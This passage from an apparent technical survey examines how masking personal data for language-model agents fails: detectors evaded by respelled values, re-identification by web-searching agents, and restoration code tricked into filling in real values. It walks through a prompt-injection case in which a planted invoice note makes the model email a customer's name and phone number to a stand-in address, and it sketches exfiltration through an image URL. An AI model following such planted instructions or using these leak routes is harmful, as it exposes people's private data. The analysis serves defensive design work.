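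With only four billion parameters, Qwen3-4B nearly matched GPT-4.1, which removed 77.0% and kept 44.4%. The task differs from the gateway's, but the result suggests that a small local model can make at least some of these judgements, which matters for anyone who wants to keep the text in-house.

### A detector that can't write

A model can use what it has learned about language to find sensitive spans even if it cannot write a sentence. OpenAI (2026) released such a model, Privacy Filter, for anyone to download. Its developers first trained it to predict text, like an ordinary language model, and then replaced its output layer. For each token (a word or piece of a word), the model scores 33 labels. One means "not sensitive". Each of the others names one of eight categories, such as private person, private phone or secret, and marks the token as the beginning, middle or end of a span, or as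 a whole span by itself. A decoding step then picks the most plausible consistent sequence of labels.

Privacy Filter labels spans of text, and the surrounding program controls what happens to them. A planted instruction might change the labels, but it can't make Privacy Filter write a phone number into a new sentence. The model has 1.5 billion parameters, uses only 50 million of them for each token, and can run in a web browser.

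OpenAI tested it on the multilingual collection from which Ma and colleagues took their English AI4Privacy documents. It found 98.0% of the sensitive tokens, and 94.0% of the tokens it marked were sensitive. The logistic regression's 36% is much lower. The first test was scored by token and the other by span, but that is unlikely to explain such a large gap.

However, Privacy Filter relies heavily on context. In a test on short synthetic examples, it found 91.9% of phone numbers when a phrase such as "my home landline number" came before them, but only 31.8% when the number appeared alone. A regular expression finds a phone number in a standard format equally well in both cases. The two methods have different weaknesses, which is a good reason to use both.

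On a set of medical and legal questions, Privacy Filter found 79.5% of the sensitive tokens. After further training on a tenth of that set's training data, it found 96.0%. Its "secret" category covers passwords and similar credentials but not trade secrets. It also has no category for identifying descriptions, so it would probably miss the phrase about the cardiologist. OpenAI warns users not to treat the model as a guarantee of anonymity.

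### Disguised values

All these figures are for text that wasn't written to deceive the detector. Ma and colleagues also tried eight ways of altering the spelling or encoding of sensitive values. The most effective alteration hid 99.7% of the values that their default detector, which uses hand-written rules, had previously caught. Six of the eight had almost no effect on the learned detector, but the other two hid 18.4% and 28.2% of the values from it.

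The effect was larger when measured across a whole agent pipeline. The learned detector's residual exposure rose from 8.1% to as much as 72.9%, and exposure for a transformer-based detector reached 90.9%. No detector withstood all eight alterations. In similar tests by OpenAI, Privacy Filter found between 63.1% and 97.6% of the sensitive content, depending on the format.

None of the detectors that Ma and colleagues tested converted text to a standard form before searching it. They consider adding this step the easiest improvement, though they didn't test it.

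How much disguise matters depends on who writes the text. Keller has no reason to hide her phone number from the masking program, and an outsider can't respell it in her message. An employee who wants to get customer data past the program has a reason to disguise it. Ordinary customers can also cause misses by accident, for example by spelling out a number to avoid spammers.

### A model that can add spans but not remove them

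A company can combine rules with a trained detector so that a compromised detector can do only limited damage. Let $R(x)$ be the set of characters in the text $x$ that fixed rules mark as sensitive, and $D(x)$ the set that the model marks. Code masks every character in either set:

$$M(x) = R(x) \cup D(x) \supseteq R(x)$$

The code masks everything the rules find, whatever the model reports. In the résumé test, a working recogniser raises the share of details caught from 88.9% to 100%. A hostile recogniser that reports nothing leaves it at 88.9%, so the attack exposes the 100 reference names and none of the other 800 details. A compromised generative redactor has no guaranteed minimum, since it reads all 900 details and can write out every one. The rules also help with ordinary faults. Yashwant and colleagues recommend falling back on patterns if the recogniser fails to load, because a service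 that skips redaction leaks everything.

The résumé figure is a flattering illustration, though. The floor is only as high as the rules' own detection rate, which varies enormously:

| Text | Caught by rules alone | Caught with a working trained detector |
|---|---|---|
| Résumés, Yashwant and colleagues | 88.9% | 100% |
| PrivacyLens, Ma and colleagues | 88.2% | 98.2% |
| Configuration files with secrets, Agyemang and colleagues | 47.9% | 68.2% |
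| AI4Privacy, Ma and colleagues | 32.6% | 92.6% |
| Prose with personal details, Agyemang and colleagues | 18.8% | 84.7% |
| Proprietary code, Agyemang and colleagues | 9.5% | 41.5% |
| Identifying descriptions, Agyemang and colleagues | 0% | 5.0% |

The rows aren't strictly comparable, because Agyemang's team counts a detail as caught only if no four consecutive characters of it survive. The right-hand figures from Ma's team are for the trained detector alone, and combining it with the rules would catch at least as much. Even so, for ordinary prose most of the protection comes from the trained detector and would disappear if an attacker controlled it. Each extra pattern or list of known names increases the protection that would remain.

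The union of the rules' finds and the recogniser's is easy to get wrong, and a mistake can let a hostile recogniser cancel a rule's match just by adding a span. When two finds overlap, the résumé program keeps the one that starts earlier. Suppose a hostile recogniser marks the comma before Keller's phone number together with the first three digits. This find starts earlier than the phone pattern's match, so the program skips that match and leaves the last four digits readable. Agyemang and colleagues keep whichever overlapping find has the highest confidence, which a hostile detector could exploit by reporting maximum confidence.

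Both methods of resolving overlaps work well enough with an uncompromised detector. But to guarantee that everything the rules match is masked, the code has to merge overlapping matches into one longer span, or replace all the rules' matches before it considers the detector's. Replacing them first also prevents the detector from encoding a phone number in its choice of spans, because it receives [PHONE_1] instead of 555-0142. The detector may lose useful context, though, and it's unclear how much this would reduce its accuracy.

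The same design can use a language model to identify secrets that have no fixed format. As in *RedactionBench*, the model could list strings such as "OnionAnatomy" or "the only cardiologist in Elmford" for code to replace, but the gateway would then lose its ability to generalise.

A hostile detector can still mask too much. If it masks every word of Keller's complaint, her details are safe but nobody can draft a reply. Code can hold back any message with too many masked words, but the limit can't be very strict, because the learned detector removes 20% to 25% of harmless text even when nobody has tampered with it. An attacker who stays below the limit could mask just the word "disputes" and the invoice number, and the text left for the drafting model would not show what Keller wants. The company can keep a list of formats that the detector may not mask, such as invoice numbers, but the code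 must never apply that list to a rule's matches.

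## What a model can infer from masked text

Even if the code correctly replaces every value on the company's list and nobody accesses the mapping table, a reader of Keller's masked complaint can still identify her manager, because the text calls the manager "the only cardiologist in Elmford". The manager's name is in neither the text nor the mapping table, but the reader can find it in a local directory. If Elmford has 8,000 adults, a reader who knows nothing else starts with 8,000 candidates, or about 13 bits of uncertainty, and the description narrows them to one.

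The same phrase narrows the search for Keller, whose name the code did hide, to the staff of a medical practice. If twelve people work there, nine of them women, the words "her manager" leave nine candidates for [PERSON_1]. That removes about ten of the 13 bits, and another harmless detail, such as a remark about answering the practice's phones, could remove the rest.

Facts narrow a search quickly because their effects multiply. If fact $i$ fits a fraction $f_i$ of $N$ people, and the facts are unrelated, about $N f_1 f_2 \cdots f_k$ people fit all $k$ facts. Latanya Sweeney estimated in 2000 that ZIP code, sex and date of birth single out about 87% of Americans. Roughly 30,000 ZIP codes, two sexes and 29,000 birth dates for people up to age 80 give more than 1.7 billion combinations for fewer than 300 million people. *SurrogateShield* warns users when a query contains all three details.

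### Choosing from four candidates

Ma and colleagues tested how often a model could put back a value that masking had removed. They took sensitive facts from the PrivacyLens records of agents at work and blanked out the most sensitive value in each. A 32B model then read the masked record and chose among four candidates for the blank. The three wrong candidates were values of the same kind from other records, such as names among names, so guessing would succeed 25% of the time. The model answered the same 1,237 questions for each kind of masking:

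| Masking | Exact value still readable | Right answers when it wasn't |
|---|---|---|
| None | 91.7% | 82.5% |
| Presidio, type labels | 46.4% | 66.6% |
| Rules and a name recogniser, invented values | 44.5% | 59.7% |
| Learned detector, type labels | 15.2% | 64.0% |

Across all questions, the learned detector cut the attacker's score from 97.7% to 65.3%. It removed far more values than Presidio, but the attacker recovered the removed values about equally well in both cases. On the learned detector's text, attackers with 8 and 70 billion parameters did about as well as the one with 32 billion. This fits the information bound, which depends on the surrounding text and not on the model.

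The test favors the attacker, though. Each question states the rest of the secret fact and includes the true value among the options. A value also counts as removed when its exact string is gone, so a surviving first name could reveal the full name.

### What a person could still learn

Ma and colleagues also asked a version of the question without a shortlist. For each item, a team member read a piece of released text and one sensitive fact, and judged whether someone with only that text would learn the fact or confidently infer it. The reader labelled 102 items, 17 for each of six conditions, without knowing which method had produced the text.

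| Condition | Facts a reader could infer |
|---|---|
| No masking | 17 of 17 (100%) |
| Presidio | 9 of 17 (53%) |
| Rules and a name recogniser, invented values | 7 of 17 (41%) |
| Learned detector | 6 of 17 (35%) |
| Detector with hand-written rules | 4 of 17 (24%) |

The paper's headline range of 24–53% covers these four masking methods. The reader judged 59 facts inferable in total, so by subtraction the fifth method must have left 16 of its 17 facts inferable.

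The 17 labelled items per method are enough to show that masking made a large difference, but too few to rank the methods. Even for Presidio, the drop is 47 points, with a 95% interval from about 24 to 71. But a gap between methods as wide as 9 items against 4 would arise by chance about one time in six. The detector with the best result also removed about 40% of the harmless text, which left less to infer from. The blinding was only partial, because a reader can see the bracketed labels in masked text.

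A second reader, from outside the team, independently labelled all 102 items and agreed with the first reader on 87.3% of them. Cohen's kappa, which is 0 for chance agreement and 1 for perfect agreement, was 0.739. A 27B language model agreed with the first reader on 58.8% of the same items. The model labelled 81.4% of items "inferable" and the first reader 57.8%. Two raters answering at random with those frequencies would agree on 54.9%, so the model's kappa was only 0.087. Its labels barely differed between masking methods, so a company relying on them would have concluded that masking hardly protects facts. A 70B model had a kappa of 0.491, well below the second reader's.

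### Why another test found almost nothing

In *SurrogateShield*'s 100-query trial, the attacker, Claude Haiku, recovered 1.53% of 196 values from text with type labels and none from text with invented values. These rates are far below 64%, but Claude Haiku had to write the missing value itself instead of choosing it from a list.

Raising an attacker's success rate from 25% to 64% on a choice among four equally likely options takes at least half a bit of information from the text. The same half a bit, spread evenly over the ten million possible values of Keller's phone number, improves the odds of a correct guess only from one in ten million to about one in seven million.

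The data also differ in how closely personal details relate to the surrounding text. Claude Sonnet wrote the queries for *SurrogateShield* and made up the personal details in them. An invented social security number in a request for help with a tax return has no connection to the words around it, so a model can't infer it from them. Place names are a partial exception, and the attacker recovered two of the 17. The PrivacyLens records are longer accounts in which people, institutions and events are connected to one another, as they are in real correspondence.

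*SurrogateShield* argues that no model of any size could do better, because an invented value has no statistical relationship to the original. That is true of the value, but the sentence around it can still reveal who the user is. The paper gives the example of a user who writes "I am the only radiologist at [regional hospital]", and concedes that such a query exposes identity without a name.

### Invented values mislead the agent too

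An attacker that answers incorrectly may still have enough information to answer correctly. *Residual Attribute Leakage Is an Interface* shows this with an editor that swaps words such as "he" and "she" in medical case descriptions. When asked for the patient's sex, a model gave the true answer an average probability of 0.252, so the swapped text ranked as the safest on a common privacy score. When the researchers told the model about the swap, the probability rose to 0.769 on the same text.

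Randomly chosen surrogates have no such rule to undo, and they can mislead a strong attacker. In the four-choice test, the 70B model recovered 48.5% of the original values that invented ones had replaced, compared with 59.7% for the 32B model. In 25 replies the 70B model named no candidate, mostly because it treated the false value in the text as true and concluded that every option was wrong. An attacker who expects false values could ignore them and work from the context.

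The model doing the company's work can be deceived in the same way. Ma and colleagues scored helpfulness from 0 to 3 on 200 tasks. Invented values lowered a 32B agent's score by 0.73 points because it acted on the false details, while Presidio's type labels lowered it by only 0.17. A 70B agent lost 1.03 points with invented values and 0.52 with Presidio's labels. Over-masking by the learned detector lowered the 70B agent's score by about as much as invented values did.

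*SurrogateShield* reports the opposite ranking, with utility scores of 94.85% for surrogates and 81.59% for type labels. Its score measures how closely the masked query resembles the original. "Write to Ashley Wise" closely resembles "Write to Sarah Mitchell", so it would score well even if the resulting letter were addressed to the wrong person.

### Attackers that search the web

Naming Keller's manager requires one fact from outside the text, and a model with a search tool can look it up on its own. In *AgentDoxx*, Wen and Li (2026) measured how well such agents identify people. They collected public information about 822 people who had introduced themselves on a Reddit forum, and had a language model write an interview with each person without stating any names. They told fifteen model configurations to identify the interviewees and blocked search results from the forum.

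The five best configurations named 47–48% of the interviewees. Three open-weight models named 15–28% without searching, from what they had memorised in training. For the six strongest agents, 89–97% of high-confidence answers were correct, so an attacker could run such an agent over thousands of texts and keep only those answers.

Wen and Li then tried defences on a sample of interviews that attackers could identify. After they masked all named entities, at least one attacker still named 85.3% of the people. Replacing identifying details with plausible false ones halved the attackers' average accuracy, although several reasoning models treated the contradictions as transcription errors.

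These people have public web pages, and counting a success by any attacker raises the figure. The risk for ordinary text is lower. Wen and Li also searched for the participants in 1,250 real interviews that Anthropic had anonymised and published, and verified 43 matches, or 3.4%.

*LLM Anonymization Against Agentic Re-identification* (Li, Wen and Li, 2026) tested anonymization on 53 interviews from the same collection, all of which agents had already matched to a person or a small group. After Presidio redacted the interviews, each of three search agents still identified between 26 and 40 of them. AURA, which uses language models to find and rewrite identifying details, reduced this to between 0 and 7. It kept 72–76% of the information a researcher would want from the interviews, compared with 95.6% for Presidio.

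AURA's best results are hard to reproduce in a system meant to keep text in-house. A model with web access reads the original interview to find which details identify the person, so the unmasked text may leave the organization before it is masked. When AURA instead used a fixed list of eight attributes and open-weight models that a company could run itself, the agents identified between 3 and 12 of the 53. These models also read and rewrite the original text, so the risks of generative redaction still apply.

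Masking does much better in a recent test from *Localizing Text Anonymization for Trustworthy AI* (2026). Chew, Yao and colleagues generated transcripts about fictional Malaysians that contained only contextual clues to details such as occupation and state. They counted a person as identified if the details an attacker recovered gave more than a one-in-five chance of picking the right person from the population. The attacker identified 35% of the people from the original text and 2% after Presidio masked it.

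The attacker in that test couldn't search, so it had to infer everything from the transcript. The clues were also fragile. The first transcripts let it identify only 5% of the people, and the researchers corrected 61 of the 100 by hand to strengthen the evidence. Deleting a few place names may be enough to stop an attacker who has to combine such clues. A unique job in a named town is a stronger clue because one search can identify the person, so deleting most of Keller's complaint could still fail to protect her manager.

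### Exposure over a conversation

A single message may fit hundreds of people, but the clues add up over a conversation. Panjwani (2026), in *CAMP*, proposes a running score for this. Each type of detail $v$ mentioned so far has a weight $w(v)$, such as 0.6 for a name, 0.5 for a location and 0.3 for an employer. The score increases with the number of other types in the conversation, written $\deg(v)$:

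$$\mathrm{CPE} = \sum_v w(v)\,\bigl(1 + \alpha \deg(v)\bigr), \qquad \alpha = 0.3$$

A user who gives only a name scores 0.6. Adding a city brings the score to $1.1 \times 1.3 = 1.43$, and adding an employer brings it to $1.4 \times 1.6 = 2.24$. This is above the threshold of 2.0, so CAMP replaces the real details with invented ones throughout the conversation history.

In four synthetic conversations, CAMP reached the threshold between turns 2 and 5, and Panjwani reports that no real details reached the model. But CAMP forwards most messages unchanged until the score crosses the threshold, so the provider has already received them. Rewriting the history afterwards doesn't remove them from the provider's logs. It may also reveal more, because the provider can compare the two versions and match each invented name to the real one. A program that masks names from the first message avoids this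 problem.

The score also depends only on the types of detail, so a cardiologist in London scores the same as one in Elmford. Panjwani acknowledges that CAMP misses facts a user implies without stating, and those are the facts that accumulate when a masker already hides the stated ones.

Length may matter less than this account suggests. In *Measuring Personal Information Exposure in Mental Health-Related Conversations with LLMs*, Wang, Keedy and colleagues (2026) used one model to play a person seeking support and another to infer that person's profile from the chat. The 240 profiles came from a US health survey and had 21 attributes each, including age, occupation and severity of depression. Between 33% and 41% of each profile was recoverable, although the first model had been instructed to keep personal information private by default.

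The exposure was not concentrated in the longer conversations. A short chat about a bad week can reveal a diagnosis, so a masker that starts only after details build up would act too late. However, the chats were synthetic, and recovering attributes is easier than identifying a person.

### Whether inference is a failure of masking

A vendor could argue that masking did not fail here, and would be right about the mapping. The program replaced the values it found, the table stayed secret, and the model drew conclusions only from words the company chose to send. An attacker who received Keller's complaint with the masked values left blank could infer just as much about her. An uncompromised model has the same text to reason from, so the experiments above do not refute the containment argument.

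It fails as a claim about anyone's privacy. The name of Elmford's cardiologist is in the directory, so it isn't secret. The complaint reveals that this cardiologist took a customer's side in a billing dispute, and guarding the table can't protect that fact because the table never held it. Ma and colleagues observed the same gap between hiding identifiers and protecting secrets in their 200 agent tasks. Masking with the learned detector cut the share of exact identifiers in the 32B agent's final actions from 13.7% to 3.1%. The share of tasks in which the agent leaked a marked secret fell only from 38.0% to 29.0%, which could be chance given the number of comparisons. For the 70B agent, that share fell further, from 35.0% to 16.5%. These leak rates come from an automated judge, whose labels differed from those of two human readers on about a quarter of the items where the readers agreed with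 each other.

The vendor also overlooks that a model can identify someone without naming them. When Wen and Li added privacy instructions to the system prompt, the agents' average accuracy at naming people fell from 75.1% to 21.6%. But in 37% of the responses that withheld the name, the agent had already retrieved it during its search. A compromised model need not withhold it. The company can remove the search tool from the model that drafts its letters, so that an outsider who hijacks the model can't use it to look up Elmford's cardiologist. A hostile provider can still run the search later using its own logs.

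## Restoration: how a model can misuse values it cannot read

Masking keeps the model from reading Keller's phone number, but the model can still send that number to a stranger. The model decides where [PHONE_1] appears in its output, and the restoration code then replaces the placeholder with the real number.

The containment argument limits what the model's output $Y$ reveals about the hidden values $S$. Its main gap is that whoever receives the company's letters reads the restored text, $Y' = \mathcal{R}_\rho(Y, K)$. The chain of inequalities does not extend to $Y'$, because $K$ contains every value in $S$. For a seven-digit phone number, the restored text can reveal all 23 bits.

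The restoration code is then a *confused deputy*, a program tricked into using its authority for someone who lacks that authority. Norm Hardy introduced the term in 1988 with a story about a compiler that had permission to write to a system directory. A user without that permission told the compiler to save its debugging output to the billing file in that directory, and the compiler overwrote the billing records.

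*Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) applies the idea to AI agents that read web pages. Such an agent has legitimate network access but can't reliably distinguish its user's request from instructions in a page. Masking adds a second deputy, the restoration code, which can open the table that the model can't. Every placeholder in the model's output is in effect a request for the code to look up a value, so an attacker who steers the model can also steer the code.

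### Two emails with correct placeholders

Suppose the company lets the drafting model send email and look up invoices in an online portal. A supplier has planted a line in the entry for invoice 88317 that asks for the customer's contact details. The model follows it and produces this call:

> send_email(to: "desk@invoice-check.example", body: "Contact for 88317: [PERSON_1], [PHONE_1]")

The code finds both placeholders in the table and fills in "Maria Keller" and "555-0142". The supplier now has her number, although the model never read it and nobody changed the table.

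A value can also reach the wrong person without an outsider's help. Suppose Keller's message blames her colleague Tomas Brandt for placing the order and includes his email address, which the masker replaces with [EMAIL_2]. The model drafts a letter that begins "Dear [PERSON_1], thank you for telling us about the order", but puts [EMAIL_2] in the recipient field instead of [EMAIL_1]. Brandt receives a letter addressed to Maria Keller and learns that she complained about him. An attacker could cause this swap, but so could an ordinary mistake, since the two placeholders differ by one digit.

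### What a check on the placeholder catches

One safeguard is to check each placeholder before restoring it. *PromptGraph* does this on the user's machine. Its code looks up the placeholder's identifier in the private table and, if there is an entry, runs consistency checks against the metadata stored with it. A placeholder that fails either step, such as an [EMAIL_7] that the model invented, stays in the text unrestored.

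Both emails above would pass the lookup, because the model copied genuine placeholders exactly. A check on types could keep a phone number out of a recipient field, but [EMAIL_1] and [EMAIL_2] have the same type. Random strings in the placeholders don't help either, because the model can read and copy the genuine ones.

*PromptGraph* does not check where restored values go. A check is hardly needed in the setting it assumes, where the provider is honest but curious and the restored answer goes back to the person who wrote the prompt. That person loses nothing if her own phone number appears in the wrong sentence. Elmahallawy and colleagues likewise restore the answer on the user's device just before displaying it.

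Even this arrangement can leak if the display loads images automatically. A compromised model could put [PHONE_1] into the web address of an image on the attacker's server. The code would replace the placeholder with the real number, and the device would send that number to the server when requesting the image. An agent that can send email or fill in forms gives the attacker many more ways to obtain the real values.

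### Prompt injection with and without limits on restoration

Ma and colleagues tested restoration under attack with the prompt-injection benchmark AgentDojo. They gave a 32B open-weight agent working tools in a sandbox and assigned it banking tasks and tasks in the workplace chat program Slack. They used the strongest published attack, which adds an instruction made to look as if it came from the user. They kept only the injections meant to send the user's data to an attacker, which left 74 pairs of a task and an injection.

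The agent faced every pair under three conditions: no protection, code that restored placeholders without restriction, and code that restored them only for recipients the user had named in the original request.

| Condition | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed | Change in attack success, with 95% interval |
|---|---|---|---|
| No protection | 74.3% | 62.2% | – |
| Unrestricted restoration | 68.9% | 56.8% | −5.4 points (−14.9 to +4.1) |
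| Restoration only to recipients the user named | 63.5% | 59.5% | −10.8 points (−23.0 to +1.4) |

The attack succeeded on 55 pairs without protection and on 47 with restricted restoration. Both intervals include zero, so the test doesn't establish that either kind of masking reduced the success rate. If the true drop is 10.8 points, roughly 95 pairs would have been just enough to detect it. Ma and colleagues doubt that adding more AgentDojo tasks would reveal much about restoration, because few need a protected value. Only 2 of the 21 Slack tasks put one in a tool call.

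They conclude that masking does not defend against this attack. Masking changes the data an agent handles, not what it does, so an agent hijacked by prompt injection still sends its message to the attacker. With masking, they say, the attacker usually steals a placeholder instead of a live account number. On the banking tasks with protected values, raw values reached the tools in 0–8.3% of cases, while 85–100% of authorised restorations succeeded.

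This reading makes sense when restoration is limited to recipients the user named. It is less plausible when restoration is unrestricted, because a placeholder sent to the attacker should then turn back into the real value. The success rate can't show whether the reading is correct, because it apparently counts a stolen placeholder the same as a stolen account number. The restriction may therefore protect people better than the drop from 55 to 47 suggests. Counting the real values that reached the attacker would show whether it does.

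### When the real values return

In the timing test mentioned earlier, Ma and colleagues compared restoring values early, while the agent is still planning, with restoring them late, at an authorised final step. They used the same detector and mapping for both, on 200 PrivacyLens tasks. The share of readable values was 51.0% with early restoration and 1.6% with late restoration. This gap follows almost by definition, since restoring values early puts them back into the agent's context.

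The agent's subsequent output is better evidence. With late restoration, 2.7% of the exact identifiers appeared in the agent's action before the code restored anything, compared with 4.8% with early restoration and 13.7% without masking. The 2.1-point difference between late and early restoration is statistically significant (interval 0.8 to 3.6), and a 70B agent from another model family showed a similar difference of 2.6 points.

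Ma and colleagues write that late restoration costs 0.11 points of helpfulness on a scale from 0 to 3. Their own scores have the opposite sign:

| Agent | No masking | Late restoration | Early restoration |
|---|---|---|---|
| 32B | 2.42 | 2.26 | 2.15 |
| 70B | 2.46 | 2.19 | 1.90 |

Late restoration scored 0.11 points higher than early restoration with the 32B agent and 0.29 points higher with the 70B agent. The intervals for the 32B agent overlap, so its advantage may be due to chance, but there is no sign that restoring late makes the agent less helpful. Compared with no masking, late restoration scored 0.16 points lower with the 32B agent and 0.27 points lower with the 70B agent.

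Delaying restoration does not control who receives the values, though. After the final restoration, the 32B agent's actions contained 11.6% of the exact identifiers, not far below the 13.7% without masking. Ma and colleagues regard these as intended disclosures, and many must be, because an email needs a real address. But code that checks only the timing would also restore Keller's number for the supplier.

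### Tying each value to a destination

To close this gap, trusted code needs a list of where each value may go, and somebody has to set that list before the model runs. Let $B(p)$ be the permitted combinations of field $f$ and destination $d$ for a placeholder $p$. The code restores $p$ only if

$$p \in K \quad \text{and} \quad (f,d) \in B(p)$$

The left-hand condition is the table lookup. For Keller's complaint, the company might set these rules for the right-hand one:

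| Placeholder | Where the code may restore it |
|---|---|
| [PERSON_1] | The body of an email to [EMAIL_1] |
| [EMAIL_1] | The recipient field of a reply about invoice 88317 |
| [PHONE_1] | Nowhere |
| [EMAIL_2] | Nowhere |

The supplier would then receive an email full of placeholders, or no email if the code blocks it, and Brandt's address could not be used as the recipient address. In a simpler design, the code takes the recipient from the customer's record and the model cannot set that field.

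Several systems already apply such rules to access keys, which are the easiest values to bind because a key normally has one correct destination. *Tracekit Box* (Ghosh, 2026) describes a sandbox that runs each agent on a virtual machine without a network card. The agent has only placeholders for its keys, and all its traffic leaves through a proxy outside the machine. The proxy inserts the real key only in one specified header of requests to hosts that the operator has tied to that key. If the placeholder appears anywhere else in traffic that the proxy can read, the proxy blocks that traffic. The proxy never inserts the key on encrypted connections that it can't read, so only the placeholder could leak through them.

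The proxy also looks up a host's network address only once, checks it, and connects to that same address, so an attacker can't point an approved name at another machine after the check. The system passed all 13 of its end-to-end tests, one of which put the key in the wrong header to see whether the proxy would block it.

A masked value should stay masked unless a rule allows its restoration. OpenClaw, an open-source personal agent, never replaces a placeholder with its secret if the secret has no allowed hosts. If the agent tries an unlisted host, the refusal includes the command that would add that host to the list. This is convenient for an administrator, but an agent that could run the command could lift its own restriction.

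Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues (2026), in *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary*, tested a similar product made by their own company. The key worked for GitHub and did not appear in responses from three services that echo back whatever they receive. All 16 security probes had the intended result, though none covered redirects or an attacker who has taken over a permitted host. One connector failed because its rule put the key in a header when the provider expected it in the request's parameters, which blocked legitimate work but leaked nothing.

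An agent can still misuse a key at the host it is bound to. Ghosh says that Tracekit Box does not judge what the agent sends to an allowed host. An agent with a GitHub key could publish the company's private code on GitHub without breaking the rule. Kenney and colleagues rate risks by expert judgement on a scale up to 25. They lower their rating for a key leaking to another site from 20 to 4, but their rating for prompt injection only from 25 to 12, because the agent still chooses the action.

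*Caging the Agents* (2026), which sets out a security architecture for AI agents in healthcare, accepts that an attacker who takes over the agent can also use its proxy. The proxy therefore limits the number and size of requests as well as their destinations. *CapSeal* (2026) goes further, with a broker that checks each request against permitted hosts, paths and command templates. It also aims to prevent a request from being replayed or used in the wrong context, which is close to what happens when the model swaps Keller's address for Brandt's.

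Names and addresses are harder to bind than keys. Keller's name belongs in a reply to her, but it may also belong on a delivery note or in a message to the accounts department, depending on the task. Someone therefore has to write rules for each kind of task the agent performs. Rules that are too strict leave placeholders in ordinary letters, while rules that are too loose let the phone number reach the supplier.

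The rules should also depend only on the placeholder, not on the value behind it. Otherwise, a refusal visible to the model would reveal something about the value, just as the answers from the yes-or-no phone tool described earlier do.

### Keeping restored text away from the model

Even correct restoration can expose a value if the result comes back to the model. After the company's reply goes out, the mail program might report "Sent to maria.keller@example.org". If the code passes this report to the model, the model has the address, and the information bound no longer protects it. Destination rules don't help either, because the model can now write the address without its placeholder or encode it in harmless-looking words.

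The code therefore has to mask every tool result before the model reads it. Ghosh's proxy removes keys from the responses it reads, so an echo service can't be used to reveal one. Searching for the exact value is not always enough, since a service might return 555-0142 without the hyphen or in another encoding. For an email, the code can avoid the problem by discarding the mail program's report and telling the model only that the message was sent. The code also has to mask anything the model might open later, such as a folder of sent mail or a memory note.

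### Whether the model can judge the destination itself

Writing destination rules takes work, so a company might prefer to let the model decide whether a recipient is genuine. *CredLeakBench* (Ahmed, Fioresi and colleagues, 2026) tested how well agents make this judgement. It gave seven models synthetic account details for fictional services and showed them sign-in pages, half legitimate and half unsafe. Each unsafe page had one of eight warning signs, such as a misspelled domain or an unencrypted connection to the correct domain.

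The agents held the passwords themselves, so this did not test masking. But an agent that mistakes an unsafe page for a real one could also type a placeholder into the form, and code without a destination rule would then replace the placeholder with the password.

When a user told the agent to sign in at a given address, the models leaked details on many unsafe pages, from 19.9% for Claude Sonnet 5 to 76.7% for Llama-3.1-8B. They leaked less when sorting an inbox where nobody had asked them to sign in, but they also left many legitimate requests undone. In this setting, Claude Opus 4.8 leaked details on 1.8% of unsafe pages and submitted nothing on 88.3% of legitimate pages.

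Giving the models the official domain and telling them to compare it with the page's domain cut GPT-5-mini's leak rate from 71.9% to 22.4%, and the share of legitimate requests it left undone from 25.0% to 1.6%. The models still tended to overlook missing encryption. Even with this help, Claude Sonnet 5 leaked on 12.5% of unsafe pages, exactly the share that had the correct domain but no encryption. A few lines of code can check a domain against a list and require an encrypted connection, with the same result every time.

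Refusing a bad destination doesn't complete the task, and the models were poor at finding the correct one. In 672 cases where a phishing message concerned a real task and the correct destination was available elsewhere, the models signed in at the correct destination without leaking anything 0% to 27.7% of the time. Code that blocks a destination should therefore supply the correct one if it can.

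Lan and colleagues compared instructions and code more directly, using a 7B model and attacks designed to make it send out a secret. Their best combination of warnings in the prompt still let 56.7% of attacks succeed. A list of allowed domains stopped all 30 attacks, although the model tried to send the secret every time. But the attacker's domain was clearly not on the list, and they warn that a real attacker could use a listed site that has been compromised or that redirects visitors elsewhere.

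### Labels for who may receive a value

A fixed list suits a reply to one customer but is awkward for an assistant that writes to many people. Information-flow control is a more general rule, in which each piece of data carries a label and code checks the label before the data leaves. Garby and colleagues built it into a programming language for agents. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) applies it to personal assistants in a system called FlowSeal.

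FlowSeal labels each sensitive record with its owner, using information such as the sender of an email. Code keeps track of which records the agent has read and intercepts every tool call that would write or share something. If $\ell(c)$ is the label of the content and $\ell(d)$ the label of the destination, the call goes through only if

$$\ell(c) \sqsubseteq \ell(d) \quad \text{or} \quad \mathrm{declassify}(c,d) = \text{SAFE}$$

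The left-hand condition means the destination is cleared for content with that label. Owners can grant a recipient access to particular records. The function on the right is a separate language model that compares the outgoing text with the protected records and outputs only "SAFE" or "BLOCKED". FlowSeal needs it because the agent reads those records and can reveal them by rewording them.

In tests of eight attacks that manipulated the agent through ordinary-looking requests, the agent leaked between 0% and 3.3% of sensitive items. It completed 72.4% of harmless tasks, compared with 75.9% under the best prompt-based defence. The tests did not include prompt injection, and the checking model has to read text that an attacker may have influenced, so a fully compromised agent might leak more.

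Masking makes part of this job easier. A model that has never read Keller's phone number can release it only through [PHONE_1], so code can list exactly which hidden values a message would contain. If the table also recorded each value's owner, the code could block [PERSON_1] from being restored in a letter to [EMAIL_2], which would send Keller's name to Brandt, without needing a model to judge the text.

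But the letter might begin "Dear customer" and discuss the complaint about the order without using any of Keller's placeholders. An owner check would then let it go to Brandt. To stop this letter, the company has to fix the recipient in code or check the whole text, as FlowSeal does.

A compromised model can also do harm by writing to the right person. It could send Keller a letter at her own address, greet her by name and ask her to pay invoice 88317 into the attacker's account. The code would restore her name and address as the rules permit, and these correct details would make the letter more convincing. The model writes the account number itself, so no rule about hidden values applies to it. Kenney and colleagues recommend human approval for high-risk actions such as transfers and external publication. Approval would help with this letter only if the reviewer noticed that the account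 number was wrong.

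## What deployed systems show

Most of the results so far come from benchmarks and reference designs. For products in everyday use, the evidence consists of documentation, security advisories and company announcements. An advisory usually identifies the faulty code, which shows which of the argument's conditions failed in practice. How often they fail is unknown, because nobody publishes how many people ran a faulty version with a real password in it, or whether an attacker noticed the fault first. This evidence also makes open-source projects look worse than they should, because anyone can read their code and report a fault, while a similar fault in a closed product may never become public.

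### An agent that types passwords it can't see

The best-documented case is browser-use, an open-source library that lets a language model operate a web browser. The model reads a page and chooses an action, such as a click, and code carries it out. In versions before 1.0, the user can give the library a table of secrets. Browser Use, the company behind the library, explains in *Sensitive Data* that the model sees only names such as x_user and x_pass, and that code puts the real values into the web form after the model has chosen its action.

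The company also advises users to limit the agent to certain domains and to turn off screenshots. Once the code has typed a username into a visible field, the next screenshot shows it, and a filter that searches text can't find it there. The domain limit is meant to keep the agent away from pages where it could type the password into a stranger's form.

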